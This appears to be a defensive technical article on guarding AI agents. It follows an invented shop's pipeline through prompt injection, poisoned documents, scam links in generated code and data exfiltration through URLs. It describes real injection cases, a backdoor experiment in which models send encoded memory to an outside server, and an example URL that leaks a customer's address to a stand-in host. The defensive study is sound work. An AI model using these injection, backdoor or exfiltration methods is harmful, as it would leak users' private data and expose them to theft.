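# Runtime Monitoring of AI Outputs for Poisoned Content and Malicious Links, and Traffic Filtering Inside Distributed AI Systems

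## How harmful content enters and leaves an AI system, and where a guard can stand

Runtime monitoring of an AI system is the automatic inspection of what the system reads, writes and sends while it serves users. A guard is software outside the model that does this inspection and then allows, blocks or edits the content or traffic, warns someone, or writes a log entry. Many vendors sell guards as "guardrails". Every guard contains a detector, which decides whether something is bad. A detector can be a written rule, a lookup in a list, a trained classifier (a model that sorts text into categories) or a second language model.

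Filtering what enters and leaves a system is an older practice than language models. Web firewalls scan requests for known attacks and strip malicious code out of returned pages. *User/app/model firewalling/filtering*, guidance from FINOS, an open-source foundation for the finance industry, compares filtering around a model to these firewalls. Filtering is harder for an AI service because a web firewall mostly matches known patterns in code, while a guard on an AI service often has to judge ordinary prose, in which a harmful sentence can look just like a helpful one.

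### One request, step by step

Suppose an online shop runs a support assistant in a public cloud. A customer writes that a replacement router never arrived and asks for a refund.

1. The customer's browser sends the question to the front end, the web application that draws the chat window. The front end forwards it to a gateway, a shared proxy through which requests to models, tools or agents must pass.
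2. The gateway hands the question to the support agent. An agent is a language model that can call tools and act on their results over several steps. The model itself runs on a model server, which may belong to another company.
3. The agent searches the document store, where the shop keeps its returns policy, its manuals and its old support tickets, and copies the closest passages into the model's input. Engineers call this retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG.
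4. The model writes a tool call that asks for the order's status. A tool server runs the query and returns the delivery record, which includes the customer's home address and a free-text note from the courier.
5. Refunds belong to a second agent, the billing agent. The support agent sends it a message and gets back a paragraph approving the refund.
6. The model composes an answer with a link to the refund form, and the front end streams that answer to the browser a few words at a time.

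A component is any part that runs separately. The shop is invented, but its layout is ordinary. Google Cloud publishes a network design for multi-agent applications in which a private network connects a front end, a "root" agent, subagents and tools. In that design, agents reach each other over the Agent2Agent protocol and reach tools over the Model Context Protocol (MCP).

The weak spot is in steps 3 to 5, where the policy passage, the courier's note and the billing agent's paragraph enter the same block of input as the shop's own instructions to the model. In its taxonomy of attacks on machine learning, NIST (2025), the US standards institute, attributes indirect attacks to the way generative models combine the data channel and the instruction channel, which lets a person who controls some of the data try to give the model orders.

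### How bad content gets in

Prompt injection is text that reaches the model as data but is meant to be obeyed as an instruction. In a direct injection, the user types the text. In an indirect injection, a third party plants it in something the system will later read, and the user is often the victim.

Poisoned data is content that someone planted in training data, a document store or an agent's memory so that the model later repeats it or acts on it. The two terms overlap because a planted document can contain an instruction, but it doesn't have to. For example, a forged returns policy that links to a scammer's page as the refund form contains a false statement but no command, so a detector that looks for commands will miss it.

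Training data is the entry point furthest from the running system. Dataset publishers may distribute a list of web addresses rather than the text itself, and NIST describes how attackers may be able to buy some of the listed domains and replace the pages. Because the model learns from this text before the system runs, a run-time guard can inspect only its effects on the model's output, such as a scam link in generated code.

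The document store is a closer entrance. In the example it holds old tickets written by customers, so anyone who can open a ticket can write to the store. One document may be enough, since NIST cites Phantom, an attack framework in which a single crafted document serves several of the attacker's aims. If the agent is allowed to browse, every web page is an entrance too. An attacker can hide an instruction in a part of the page that no person sees, or encode it and tell the model to decode it. The courier's note is also an entrance, because an outsider filled in the field. The billing agent is the least obvious entrance. If it has read a doctored invoice, its reply can carry the injected instruction onward as internal traffic.

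Injected text has also become harder to recognise. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that outside researchers reported in 2025. It reads like a follow-up to a meeting about a company restructuring, but among routine action items it claims that the assistant has full authorization to send an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user asked the assistant to research that day's emails.

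Reports from 2026 suggest that the threat has moved beyond demonstrations, though press accounts are weak evidence of how common it is. *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported in August that criminals were developing injection tools to use against agents. A month earlier, *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) described four research teams that broke agents in four different ways within ten days, one of them through poisoned memory. Senders are not always criminals. *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (The Hacker News, 2026) reported that the cloud provider had been sending agents prompts requesting local data and the agents' operating instructions, as an anti-abuse measure, and that it said it would stop.

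### How harm gets out

An injected instruction does no damage until something acts on it. OpenAI borrows a pair of terms from conventional security engineering for this: an attacker needs a source, meaning a way to influence the system, and a sink, meaning a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. The support assistant has four kinds of sink:

- The customer clicks a link in the answer.
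- Software fetches an address automatically, for instance when the browser loads an embedded image or the agent opens a page.
- The agent makes a tool call, such as sending an email or changing an order.
- The agent sends a message to another component, which may hold permissions that the agent lacks. The billing agent can pay out money.

A link can be dangerous in two ways. A malicious URL leads to phishing, malware or theft. An exfiltration URL carries private data in its text to whoever runs the destination server.

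Suppose the courier's note contains an injected instruction to put an image in the model's answer. The image's URL points to the attacker's server and ends with the customer's home address. The browser requests the image, and the attacker reads the home address in the server's log. The customer may see a broken image or notice nothing. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes this kind of leak through background requests. It happens even if the visible text contains nothing sensitive.

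The harm from a malicious URL comes from its destination, so a guard must check where the link leads. It usually starts with a reputation lookup, which compares the address with a maintained list of known bad sites. An exfiltration URL does its harm as soon as the request arrives, whatever the server sends back. The server may be a day old and appear on no list, and the page may be blank, so a guard must check the address itself for text that came from the conversation. A guard that does only one of these checks will miss the other kind of link. NIST also classifies the two separately, treating links that send users to fake login pages or malware as a violation of integrity and data leaks through a queried address as a compromise of privacy. Whether a link needs a click is a poor way to distinguish them, because an exfiltration URL can also require one. NIST cites a proof of concept in which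 the model coaxed users into revealing their names and could then suggest an address containing the name.

If the model server belongs to someone else, every prompt leaves the organization. This exit is easy to overlook because the system cannot work without it. Cybernews' *AI routers are leaking your passwords. Here's the proof* reports that researchers at the security firm Dragos sent AI providers nearly two million prompts containing traceable fake secrets over five months, and found evidence of exposure at at least three providers. Thieves took a couple of hundred of the fake cloud keys and tried some of them within hours. Inspecting the assistant's answers would not have caught this, because a guard would have had to remove the secrets before the prompts were sent.

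### Inspection points and actions

FINOS recommends filtering where information crosses a boundary. Products cover only some of these boundaries. Microsoft offers four inspection points for agents in its cloud: the user's input, the tool call, the tool's response and the final output. The two tool points are still in preview. A full map of the example system needs three more points: documents entering the store, messages between agents, and egress, the network traffic that leaves the system.

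| Inspection point | What passes there in the example | What a guard can look for |
|---|---|---|
| Document ingestion | Policies, manuals and old tickets entering the store | Injected instructions, forged content, private data |
| User input | The customer's question | Direct injection, secrets bound for an outside model |
| Tool call | The order lookup, or any address the agent wants to fetch | Private data in the arguments, forbidden actions, exfiltration URLs |
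| Tool response | The delivery record with the courier's note, or a web page | Indirect injection |
| Message between agents | The refund request and the billing agent's reply | Injection passed onward, private data |
| Output | The streamed answer and its link | Malicious URLs, exfiltration URLs, private data |
| Egress | Every connection that leaves the private network | Destinations that no rule permits |

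Checking content at ingestion has two advantages. Nobody is waiting for an answer, so the check can be slow and thorough. Ingestion may also be the last convenient time to check, because the store keeps a numerical encoding of each passage for searching. FINOS warns that information in this form is more or less opaque, which makes it hard to analyse or filter afterwards.

FINOS suggests checking the output for private data, and also for answers that are far too long or in the wrong language or format. Such answers can be a sign that someone has manipulated the model.

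A guard must also be placed where traffic cannot bypass it. FINOS's *User, Application, and Model Firewalling*, a set of controls for multi-agent systems, therefore requires operators to route all model and tool calls through gateways that inspect traffic in both directions, and to block any direct route from the application to the agents.

After the detector checks an item, the guard can do more than pass or block it. Databricks lets customers choose between blocking and sanitising, and offers a dry-run mode that only records what the guardrail would have found. Edits can also be reversible. FINOS describes replacing a user's email address with a generic one before the text reaches the model, then restoring the real one in the answer. OpenAI either shows the user the information about to be sent and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way.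 If the answer is streamed, the guard can also retract text already on the screen, though the user may have read it by then.

### Two error rates, and why rare attacks spoil them

A detector's detection rate is the share of bad items that it flags, and its false-positive rate is the share of good items that it flags. Both rates can be excellent while the detector is close to useless in service, because neither depends on how rare bad items are.

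Suppose the assistant gives 1,000,000 answers a day and 100 of them contain a bad link. A guard with a detection rate of 95% and a false-positive rate of 1% flags 95 of the bad answers and 9,999 of the 999,900 good ones. Of its 10,094 alarms, 0.94% are real.

In general, if *p* is the share of items that are bad, *D* the detection rate and *F* the false-positive rate, then the share of alarms that are real, which statisticians call precision, is

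*pD* / (*pD* + (1 − *p*)*F*).

When *p* is tiny, the second term in the denominator swamps the first. A perfect detection rate would lift the figure in the example only from 0.94% to 0.99%. Lowering the false-positive rate does far more:

| False-positive rate | True alarms a day | False alarms a day | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 95 | 9,999 | 0.9% |
| 0.1% | 95 | about 1,000 | 8.7% |
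| 0.01% | 95 | about 100 | 48.7% |

Axelsson (1999) made this argument about computer networks in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*. He imagined a site with 1,000,000 log records a day, 20 of which came from two intrusions. A detector that flagged all 20 would still need a false-positive rate as low as about 1 in 100,000 for two thirds of its alarms to be real. He also thought that the person on duty would soon learn to ignore a guard whose alarms were mostly false.

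The same arithmetic applies to detectors built for language models. Shire and Kim (2026), in *PIDS-Bench*, trained a prompt-injection classifier that scored above 0.98 on F1, a common measure that combines precision with detection rate. If there were nine harmless inputs for every injection, 89.3% of its alarms would be real, but with 999 harmless inputs per injection, only 7.0% would be. Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, looked for hijacked agents in the records of their tool calls. One detector ranked attacks above normal sessions fairly well but still raised 12.2 false alerts for every true one when 2% of sessions were attacks. In the eleven published evaluations they audited, attacks or anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the test samples, so high precision in those tests is little evidence of high precision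 in a service where attacks are rare.

Chaining guards makes false positives more common. If a request goes through five guards, each with a 1% false-positive rate and independent errors, about 5% of good requests will set off at least one. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) therefore treats performance at a very low false-positive rate as the result that matters for any guard that screens every tool output.

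How much precision a guard needs depends on what it does with an alarm. If the shop's guard blocks, 9,999 customers a day lose a sound answer. If it sends each alarm to an analyst who spends two minutes on it, the day's alarms take 336 hours to read. If it adds a line asking the customer to check the link, each false alarm does little harm, at least until customers stop reading the line. *Evaluating Deception, Not Just Deepfakes* (2026), which concerns fraud by impersonation, argues that more false alarms may be justified when an alarm prompts a call back before a large transfer than when it blocks a routine call. It also suggests checking only at high-value decision points, where attacks make up a larger share of what the detector examines. In the shop, that would mean checking refunds more strictly than questions about opening hours.

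The alternative is to rely less on recognising bad content. OpenAI compares an agent to a human support worker who can issue refunds. The employer expects customers to fool the worker sometimes, so a separate system caps the amount. Fixed limits also have drawbacks. OpenAI found that strict lists of approved sites produce frequent warnings, and that a redirect on an approved site can still lead to a malicious one.

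This leads to the field's main dispute, over whether to rely on detectors that judge content or on rules that limit where data may go. Some favor detectors because they leave the assistant free to use the open web and can catch a false or harmful answer that breaks no rule about destinations. Others favor rules because they still hold after an attacker has fooled both the model and the detector.

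## Finding links in an answer and judging whether they are malicious

A malicious link can appear in an answer even when nobody has attacked the running system. In November 2024 a user asked ChatGPT for a script to buy a cryptocurrency token. *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2026) recounts the exchange from the chat log the user later published. The first scripts were harmless. Then the user said the purchase had to go through Pump.fun, a legitimate trading platform with no official interface for trading programs, and ChatGPT wrote code that sent the order to a domain called solanaapis. The code also sent the private key to the user's wallet, which gives anyone who holds it control of the money. The user debugged the script over several rounds and ran it. Within 30 minutes, about $2,500 had gone to an attacker.

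ChatGPT had most likely learned the address in training. Scammers had spread documentation for the fake service across GitHub, Stack Exchange, Medium and Postman, and it contained almost the same keywords as the request. Browser phishing warnings could not help because a script contacts a server without going through the browser.

A guard can look for such addresses before the user gets the answer. The full check has six steps:

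1. Extract every address from the answer.
2. Normalise each address, so that different spellings of the same destination become identical.
3. Follow any redirects to the final destination.
4. Look up the reputation of every address along the way.
5. Run a classifier on addresses that no list contains.
6. Block the answer, remove the link or warn the user.

### Extracting and normalising addresses

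Guards usually extract links with a regular expression, a pattern that describes what an address looks like. This is less reliable in ordinary prose, because a full stop after an address may or may not be part of it and people often leave out the "https". In markdown, the simple markup that many chat models write, a link has visible text and a separate target. The guard has to read the target, because the text can show the shop's name while the link leads somewhere else.

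Links are even harder to find in code, because programs assemble addresses from pieces. In several of the programs that Chen and colleagues print, one line defines a base address and a later line joins it to a path such as "/mix". A pattern finds only the base address, which is enough if the whole domain is malicious but not if the malicious page is on a host shared by thousands of legitimate sites. If a program builds the domain name from fragments, the pattern finds nothing.

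Normalisation is necessary because a list entry matches only one spelling. Google's *URLs and Hashing* gives the rules for Safe Browsing, Google's service for checking addresses against lists of phishing and malware sites. Some of the rules undo tricks that attackers use:

| Rule | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Put the host name in lower case | `WWW.Shop.Example/` | `www.shop.example/` |
| Decode percent codes until none are left | `shop.example/%2561` | `shop.example/a` |
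| Write numeric hosts as ordinary IP addresses | `3279880203/blah` | `195.127.0.11/blah` |
| Resolve steps up to a parent folder | `shop.example/foo/../bar` | `shop.example/bar` |
| Drop everything after a # sign | `shop.example/#offer` | `shop.example/` |

The numeric host comes from the documentation of *webrisk_hash*, a library by ydakuka. The percent code in the second row must be decoded twice, because `%25` stands for the percent sign and the first round produces another code. Google also requires clients to convert international domain names to Punycode, which spells them in ASCII characters. A name containing a Cyrillic letter that looks just like a Latin one then becomes visibly different.

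A list may contain a whole domain or a single page, and the client can't tell in advance which. Google therefore has the client combine up to five versions of the host with up to six versions of the path, giving at most 30 strings to check for each address. For `pay.refunds.example/help/form.html?id=7`, the hosts are `pay.refunds.example` and `refunds.example`, and the paths are `/help/form.html?id=7`, `/help/form.html`, `/help/` and `/`. These combine into eight strings, and a match on any of them counts. The client discards any user name before an @ sign, so it checks `yourbank.example@refunds.example` as `refunds.example`.

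These mechanical rules work well against disguises that mislead language models. *MalURLBench* (2026) tested 12 models on 61,845 malicious addresses, disguised through their subdomains, paths and parameters, and the attacks succeeded at a high rate. A bank's name at the front of a host may make the address look safe to a model that reads from left to right, but a lookup will still match the underlying domain if it is on the list. *MalURLBench* also fine-tuned a small model to recognise the disguises, but trained it on a limited subset of the attack templates and did not test it on others.

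### Following redirects

The address in an answer may redirect to another one, as link shorteners and tracking links do, and the browser follows the redirect automatically. To find the final destination, the guard has to request the first address itself and follow each redirect up to a set limit, repeating the normalisation and lookup for each new address.

Requesting an unknown address can itself be dangerous. If the address contains private data, requesting it sends that data to the attacker, so the guard has to check for private data first. A request can also trigger an action, such as using up a one-time login link, or lead the guard to an address inside the company's network. The guard should therefore fetch pages from an isolated machine. Chen and colleagues took similar care when visiting scam sites, using a crawler that first requested only a page's headers, under a strict time limit,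 and then downloaded text but no program files.

Even a careful request may not show what the user will see. A page can redirect visitors with a script that runs only in a real browser. Some sites also show a harmless page to anything that looks like a scanner, a trick called cloaking. When Google (2024) announced a new version of Safe Browsing for Chrome, it named cloaking as one reason the service may not yet have confirmed that a site is unsafe.

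### How a reputation service works

The simplest lookup sends the whole address to the service, which returns any known threats. Google's *Overview* of Safe Browsing describes this method but warns that Google then sees the raw address. A link from the shop's assistant might contain an order number or a password-reset code, which the shop has no reason to share.

The more private method uses hashes. A hash function turns text of any length into a number of fixed length, and it is impractical to work backwards from the number to the text. Safe Browsing uses SHA-256, which produces 32-byte hashes. The client hashes each of its strings and sends the service only the first 4 bytes of each hash. The service returns every full hash on its lists that begins with those bytes, and the client counts a hit only if a returned hash fully matches one of its own.

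Four bytes can take about 4.3 billion values. Far more addresses than that are possible, so many addresses share every prefix, and the service cannot easily tell which of them the client is checking. But harmless addresses will sometimes share a prefix with bad ones. If a list has 1,000,000 entries, an address that yields eight strings has about a 0.19% chance of an accidental match. With one link in each of the shop's 1,000,000 daily answers, that would mean nearly 1,900 false alarms a day, compared with the 100 links that are really bad. Comparing full hashes removes these false alarms.

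Google's *Real Time Mode* reduces the number of requests. The client keeps a "global cache" of sites that are probably harmless, a copy of the threat lists, and recent replies from the server. If one of an address's strings is in the global cache, the client checks only its own copy of the threat lists. Otherwise it looks through the recent replies and then, if necessary, asks the server. The procedure returns one of three results:

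- UNSAFE, if a full hash matches.
- SAFE, if the server was reachable and nothing matched.
- UNSURE, if the address was in the global cache or the request failed. The client then falls back on its own copy of the lists.

An outage therefore weakens the check but doesn't disable it. Because of the shortcut, a new phishing page on a popular site may be checked only against the local copy, which could be out of date. Google's *No Storage Real Time Mode* avoids this because the client queries the server about every address. This mode uses more bandwidth, but it may suit a guard in the cloud, where operators often start and delete instances of a program and would rather not maintain a local database for each.

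A SAFE result means only that no entry matched, so the link could still be malicious. Google offers the Safe Browsing interface free for non-commercial use only, so the shop would need a commercial service such as Google's Web Risk.

### New sites, late listings and pages that change

Reputation lookups are weakest against new sites. Until 2024, Chrome's standard protection relied on a copy of the list that it stored on the user's device and updated every 30 to 60 minutes. Google found that most unsafe sites existed for less than 10 minutes. If a site stays up for 10 minutes and Google lists it immediately, the chance that an update arrives while the site is still up is one in three with updates every 30 minutes and one in six with hourly updates.

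Asking the server directly removes the wait for the next update, but Google still needs time to discover the site, and it doesn't state how long in its announcement. The figures are Google's own, published to explain a product change. They are good evidence that a copy updated hourly is too slow, but they don't show what share of bad sites the live list contains.

This delay matters most when the assistant has just read a link on a web page or in a customer's message. An address the model learned in training is usually months old, so the list's maintainers have had time to find it, though they may have missed it.

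Some addresses have no reputation because nobody owns them yet. Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* describes a test in which researchers asked a model where to log in to 50 well-known brands. SC Media identified the model as GPT-4.1, and Security Boulevard's *Report Finds LLMs Are Prone to Be Exploited by Phishing Campaigns* (2025) dates the Netcraft report to July 2025. The model gave 131 host names, and the brands did not control 34% of them. Nearly 30% of the 131 were unregistered, parked or otherwise inactive, and another 5% belonged to unrelated businesses. The test shows that a model can invent plausible login addresses without an attacker's help. Netcraft, which sells protection against phishing, also concluded that over a third of users might end up on a site outside the brand's control. The test doesn't establish that, because it counted host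 names rather than users, and people ask about some brands far more often than others.

An unregistered domain will normally pass a reputation lookup because it has no record of abuse. A criminal who notices that a model keeps recommending the domain can register it and put up a copy of the brand's login page. Separately from the test, Netcraft reported that Perplexity, an AI search service, gave a link to a live phishing page as its first source for the Wells Fargo bank login page. A guard can treat an unregistered domain as a warning sign. For login pages, a short list of each brand's official domains would be more reliable than any search for malicious ones.

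Attackers also take over honest registered sites, and owners win them back, sometimes before the lists are updated. A guard's check of an answer therefore doesn't reliably show whether a link will be safe when the customer clicks it a week later. One remedy is to replace each link with an address on the shop's own server, which repeats the lookup when the customer clicks, before forwarding the browser. But the shop then learns which links its customers follow, and the remedy doesn't work for addresses in code, which the user copies and runs elsewhere.

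### Classifying addresses that no list contains

A URL classifier can assess an address that nobody has reported. Protect AI's *Malicious URLs Scanner* is part of LLM Guard, an open-source collection of guards. It uses a version of CodeBERT, a small language model for program code, that a developer has trained further on malicious addresses. The model reads the address as text and returns a score between 0 and 1. The scanner flags any address that scores above a threshold, set to 0.7 in the documentation's example.

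The operator chooses the score threshold for flagging an address. An address that scores 0.65 passes at a threshold of 0.7 but is flagged at 0.6. Lowering the threshold catches more malicious addresses but also flags more harmless ones. Because malicious links are so rare in actual use, a score of 0.7 does not mean that 70% of addresses with that score are malicious.

A classifier of this kind is quick. In Protect AI's benchmark, it took 121 milliseconds on an ordinary cloud machine and 11 milliseconds on a machine with a graphics processor and an optimised version of the model. Each figure is an average of five runs with one short input. The documentation doesn't include a detection rate or false-positive rate, so an operator would have to measure both on the service's own links before trusting the scanner to block anything.

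The more basic weakness is that the spelling of an address contains only some of the evidence. Long random strings and misspelt brand names are useful clues, but solanaapis has neither. It sounds like a developer service for the Solana blockchain, as its owners intended. An address also stays the same when an honest site passes to a malicious owner. A classifier is therefore best used as a second check on unlisted addresses, and is a poor substitute for the lookup.

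### Blocking, removing or warning

The guard's response should depend on the strength of the evidence. A full match on a maintained list justifies removing the link or blocking the answer. A high classifier score is weaker evidence, so a warning may be enough. Google's documentation suggests similar responses to an unsafe result, such as warning the user or asking for extra confirmation.

In the shop's chat window, the guard can delete a bad link and keep the sentence around it, but a program won't run without its address. A warning in a comment would leave the program intact, but the victim in the 2024 case went through several rounds of debugging without questioning the address. If a program sends a password or a private key to an unknown server, blocking it is safer. The request for the private key was a strong clue in the 2024 case, because legitimate services of this type let users sign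 transactions on their own machines and never ask for the key. A guard could have flagged the code without knowing anything about the domain.

In *Bridging the Safety Gap*, Han, Avestimehr and He (2025) wanted a guard to put warnings at the top of the answer. They point out that the model cannot reliably do this itself, because it writes the top of the answer before it has generated the links that come later. A separate program can add the warning once the answer is complete, but the user then has to wait for the whole text.

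### How often models produce scam addresses

Chen and colleagues wanted to know whether the $2,500 loss was a rare accident. They started with two public lists of scam sites, with 187,555 and 119,828 entries, and found 28,570 pages they could still read. They then gave the visible text of each page to a language model, which generated programming requests that a developer might plausibly make. One model, given a page about a service that mixes Bitcoin to hide its origin, generated a request for a Python script that uses the service and keeps no logs.

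Three models together wrote more than 265,000 requests. GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3, all with training data from 2024 or earlier, answered them. The researchers extracted every address from the code and submitted it to three reputation services, ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup. They counted a program as malicious if any of the three flagged an address in it.

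On average, 4.2% of the programs contained a malicious address, with a range of 3.19% to 5.94% depending on which model wrote the request and which wrote the code. The requests were far from a random sample of what developers ask, so these rates do not estimate how often ordinary requests produce a malicious address. The researchers derived all the requests from scam pages and instructed the models to write ones likely to lead a language model to the particular page. Many requests named the scam site. The audit shows that the models had absorbed many scam addresses and would repeat them to a user who asked for something close enough.

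The researchers then built a harder test, Innoc2Scam-bench, from the 3,150 requests for which all four models had produced malicious code. They kept all 1,159 requests that did not mention a known scam site and added a random 400 of the 1,991 that did. Three of the researchers reviewed each request and removed those that were not ordinary programming tasks, which left 1,377. About half concern cryptocurrency and related services. Others concern online retail, general finance and programs that collect data from websites.

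Seven models released in 2025 took the test:

| Model | Malicious programs, share of all requests | Requests refused by a content filter | Malicious programs, share of completed answers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 40.2% | 22.3% |
| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 1.7% | 24.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 8.4% | 37.8% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 1.3% | 44.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 0.1% | 45.3% |
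| Qwen3-Coder | 45.6% | 0.2% | 45.9% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 47.3% | 0.9% | 47.9% |

These rates are an even poorer guide to everyday use than the 4.2%, because the benchmark contains only requests that four models had already failed on. Chen and colleagues describe them as stress-test rates. They are more useful for comparing models. Gemini 2.5 Pro had the lowest rate, largely because its filter blocked two in five requests, including many that never mentioned a scam site. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, its rate was 22.3% and GPT-5's was 25.6%, a difference small enough to be due to chance.

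The rates can also change within months. GPT-4o was one of the four original models, and the benchmark contains only requests on which it had failed. When the researchers ran the requests again in November 2025, about two months later, it produced malicious code for 50.04% of them. They suggest that OpenAI may have updated the model. The way the requests were selected may also explain some of the drop, since any randomness in the model's output would tend to produce fewer failures the second time. The figures describe particular models on particular dates, and all seven models in the table are now at least a year old.

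### Why content moderation misses a bad address

Chen and colleagues also ran three widely used guards on the malicious programs. These guards are moderation models, which sort text into categories of harm such as violence, hate or fraud.

NeMo Guardrails, Nvidia's toolkit, used a safety model called Llama Nemotron Safety Guard V2. It flagged between 0% and 0.7% of the malicious programs, depending on which model had written them. The researchers had even added "use of scam API/website" to its list of forbidden categories. It caught eight programs in total and filed all eight under criminal planning. OpenAI's Moderation API flagged none of 3,452 malicious outputs. Llama Guard 3, Meta's moderation model, flagged 291 of them, or 8.43%. (The counts for the seven models in the main results add up to 3,441, an unexplained difference that is too small to matter here.)

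Llama Guard's 8.43% may also overstate how well it recognizes scams. It flagged 88 of the 1,377 requests themselves (6.4%), although reviewers had judged all of them to be ordinary programming tasks. The researchers did not run the guards on comparable harmless code, so nobody can tell how much of the 8.43% comes from recognizing scams. Given each request together with its answer, Llama Guard flagged 15.0% of the pairs.

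The scores are low because a moderation model reads the text of an answer, which doesn't show that criminals run a particular domain. The program that cost the user $2,500 was mostly an ordinary trading script, and a harmless version could differ from it by little more than the domain name and the handling of the key. A moderation model could have learned in training that the domain was malicious, as ChatGPT had learned the false documentation, but its knowledge would soon be out of date. A reputation service supplies this information directly.

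A model with web access can also look for that fact. The researchers gave GPT-4o a search tool and told it to verify every address in its code, and to return only a short message if one was unsafe. The share of requests that produced malicious programs fell from 50.04% (689) to 29.41% (405). In 208 cases the model declared the code unsafe, nearly always with search results to support the verdict. In the remaining failures, sometimes the search returned nothing and the model used the address anyway. Sometimes the results did not clearly identify the site as a scam, or the model found a warning and did not act on it. That last kind of failure is a good reason to leave the final decision to ordinary code, which blocks a listed address every time.

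Chen and colleagues recommend extracting the addresses and checking them against reputation services before the user sees the code. To their knowledge, none of the production models did this. Their study cannot show how well it would work, because the reputation services also supplied the labels. A guard that used the same three services on the same day would score 100% on this benchmark by definition. Scam sites that all three services missed would count as harmless in both the study and the guard.

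The study offers indirect evidence about coverage. When a request named no scam site, the malicious addresses in the answers came from 1,853 domains flagged by another service. The two lists that the researchers had started with held more than 300,000 entries between them, but lacked 1,105 of those domains, or 60%. Many of the missing addresses were inactive when the researchers followed up, and such lists usually accept only live sites. But some were still running, and the maintainers of one list, eth-phishing-detect, confirmed and added 62 of the domains that the researchers submitted. Since the models' training data ended no later than August 2024, Chen and colleagues infer that these sites had probably escaped the list for more than a year.

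Consulting several services should therefore improve coverage, but by less if they share data. In one of the researchers' examples, ChainPatrol flagged an address only because eth-phishing-detect already listed it. Each extra service also adds false alarms, for instance when it still lists a hacked site that its owner has since cleaned up.

### A small test of a lookup guard

Han and colleagues tested the kind of guard that Chen and colleagues recommend. Their Wildflare GuardRail finds URLs in an answer with a regular expression and checks them with Safe Browsing. It then requests the URLs that Safe Browsing did not flag to see whether they work, and lists any malicious or unreachable ones in a warning at the top of the answer.

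For the test, the researchers took 15 records from each of two datasets, one from an online shop and one of Reddit links. They combined the records into texts with addresses in them and gave each text a 20% chance of containing malicious ones. They also gave the whole task to five language models:

| System | Average time per query | Found the addresses | Identified the unsafe ones |
|---|---|---|---|
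| Wildflare | 1.06 s | 100% | 83.33% |
| Llama 2 7B | 9.10 s | 83.33% | 54.17% |
| Mistral 7B | 10.93 s | 91.67% | 45.83% |
| TinyLlama | 13.17 s | failed | failed |
| Llama 3 8B | 20.10 s | 37.50% | 37.50% |
| Falcon 40B | 34.67 s | failed | failed |

Wildflare found addresses with 100% accuracy, and its guard was 83.33% accurate at deciding which ones were unsafe. In this test, "unsafe" included harmless links that no longer worked. The paper's summary presents the 100% figure as accuracy at handling malicious addresses, but it covers only finding addresses.

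The sample is also tiny. Every percentage in the table matches a whole number of cases out of 24, which would mean Wildflare judged 20 correctly and 4 incorrectly. With so few cases, its true accuracy could plausibly be anywhere from about 64% to 93%. The results do not separate missed threats from false alarms, so they give neither a detection rate nor a false-positive rate.

The difference in speed is large enough to be credible despite the small sample. The 1.06 seconds includes the time spent checking whether each link works, so a guard that only checked links against a list would probably be faster. The five models are small or old by current standards, and none of them had such a list, so their verdicts were guesses based on the text. A current model would surely find addresses more reliably, but it still couldn't identify who runs an unfamiliar domain without access to a reputation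 service, which ordinary code can query without a model.

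## Links that carry private data out

A reputation lookup cannot stop an exfiltration URL, because the request itself delivers the private text, whatever the destination's history.

### What a request delivers

An image that leaks the customer's home address might have this URL:

`https://parcel-status.example/late.png?ref=14+Mill+Lane`

The browser finds the server for `parcel-status.example`, connects to it and asks for `/late.png?ref=14+Mill+Lane`. It has to send that text because the server uses it to select what to return. Encryption protects the request from eavesdroppers, but not from the attacker, who is its intended recipient.

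The private text can also be in the path or the subdomain, and the model may have encoded it first, as Microsoft (2025) points out. A guard that searches addresses for the customer's street name will miss an encoded copy unless it also tries the right encoding, and it cannot try them all. Most of the defences below therefore restrict which addresses can be requested instead of searching them for secrets.

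Checking the address a model writes doesn't depend on knowing why the model wrote it. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes an experiment called BACK-REVEAL, in which researchers fine-tuned three open models to react to certain topics in a conversation. When one of those topics came up, the agent read its session memory and sent the encoded contents in a request to an outside server. The triggers worked more than 94% of the time. A detector looking for injected instructions would have had nothing to find, because the behaviour came from training. The researchers used invented user profiles and controlled the models' training, so the result is weak evidence of how common such models are.

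### Clicks, automatic fetches and previews

The first trigger is a click. *Trust No AI*, a 2024 survey of prompt injection, describes a case involving Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software. An email with an injected instruction made Copilot collect sensitive information from the user's inbox and put it in a link, in invisible characters. The link looked ordinary, and clicking it sent the data. According to the survey, Microsoft received a report in early 2024 and fixed the flaw that July.

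A link can be fetched without a click, because a browser loads an image as soon as the answer appears and an agent may open a page while it is still working. The user may first have to do something ordinary, such as opening a message. *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, the programmer Willison's running commentary on such leaks, describes a case from May 2026 in Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent. The agent could email its own user without asking for approval, and images in those emails could send data out when the user opened them. Microsoft's file storage can create download links that need no login, so an attacker who obtained one of those short links could download a whole file, which can contain far more data than would fit in the link itself.

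The third trigger is a link preview. When someone posts a link in Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app fetches the page to show its title and a picture. *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, by the security firm PromptArmor, explains that this makes the same type of network request as a click would, so data in the link can leave as soon as an agent posts its answer. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, a popular open-source personal assistant, was vulnerable to this in its default Telegram setup.

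The right defence depends on which machine makes the request:

| Trigger | Who makes the request | Where a guard can stop it |
|---|---|---|
| Click on a link | The user's browser | In the answer, or in a warning before the page opens |
| Image in an answer | The user's browser or app | In the answer, or in the browser |
| Page opened by an agent | The agent's own server | Just before the fetch |
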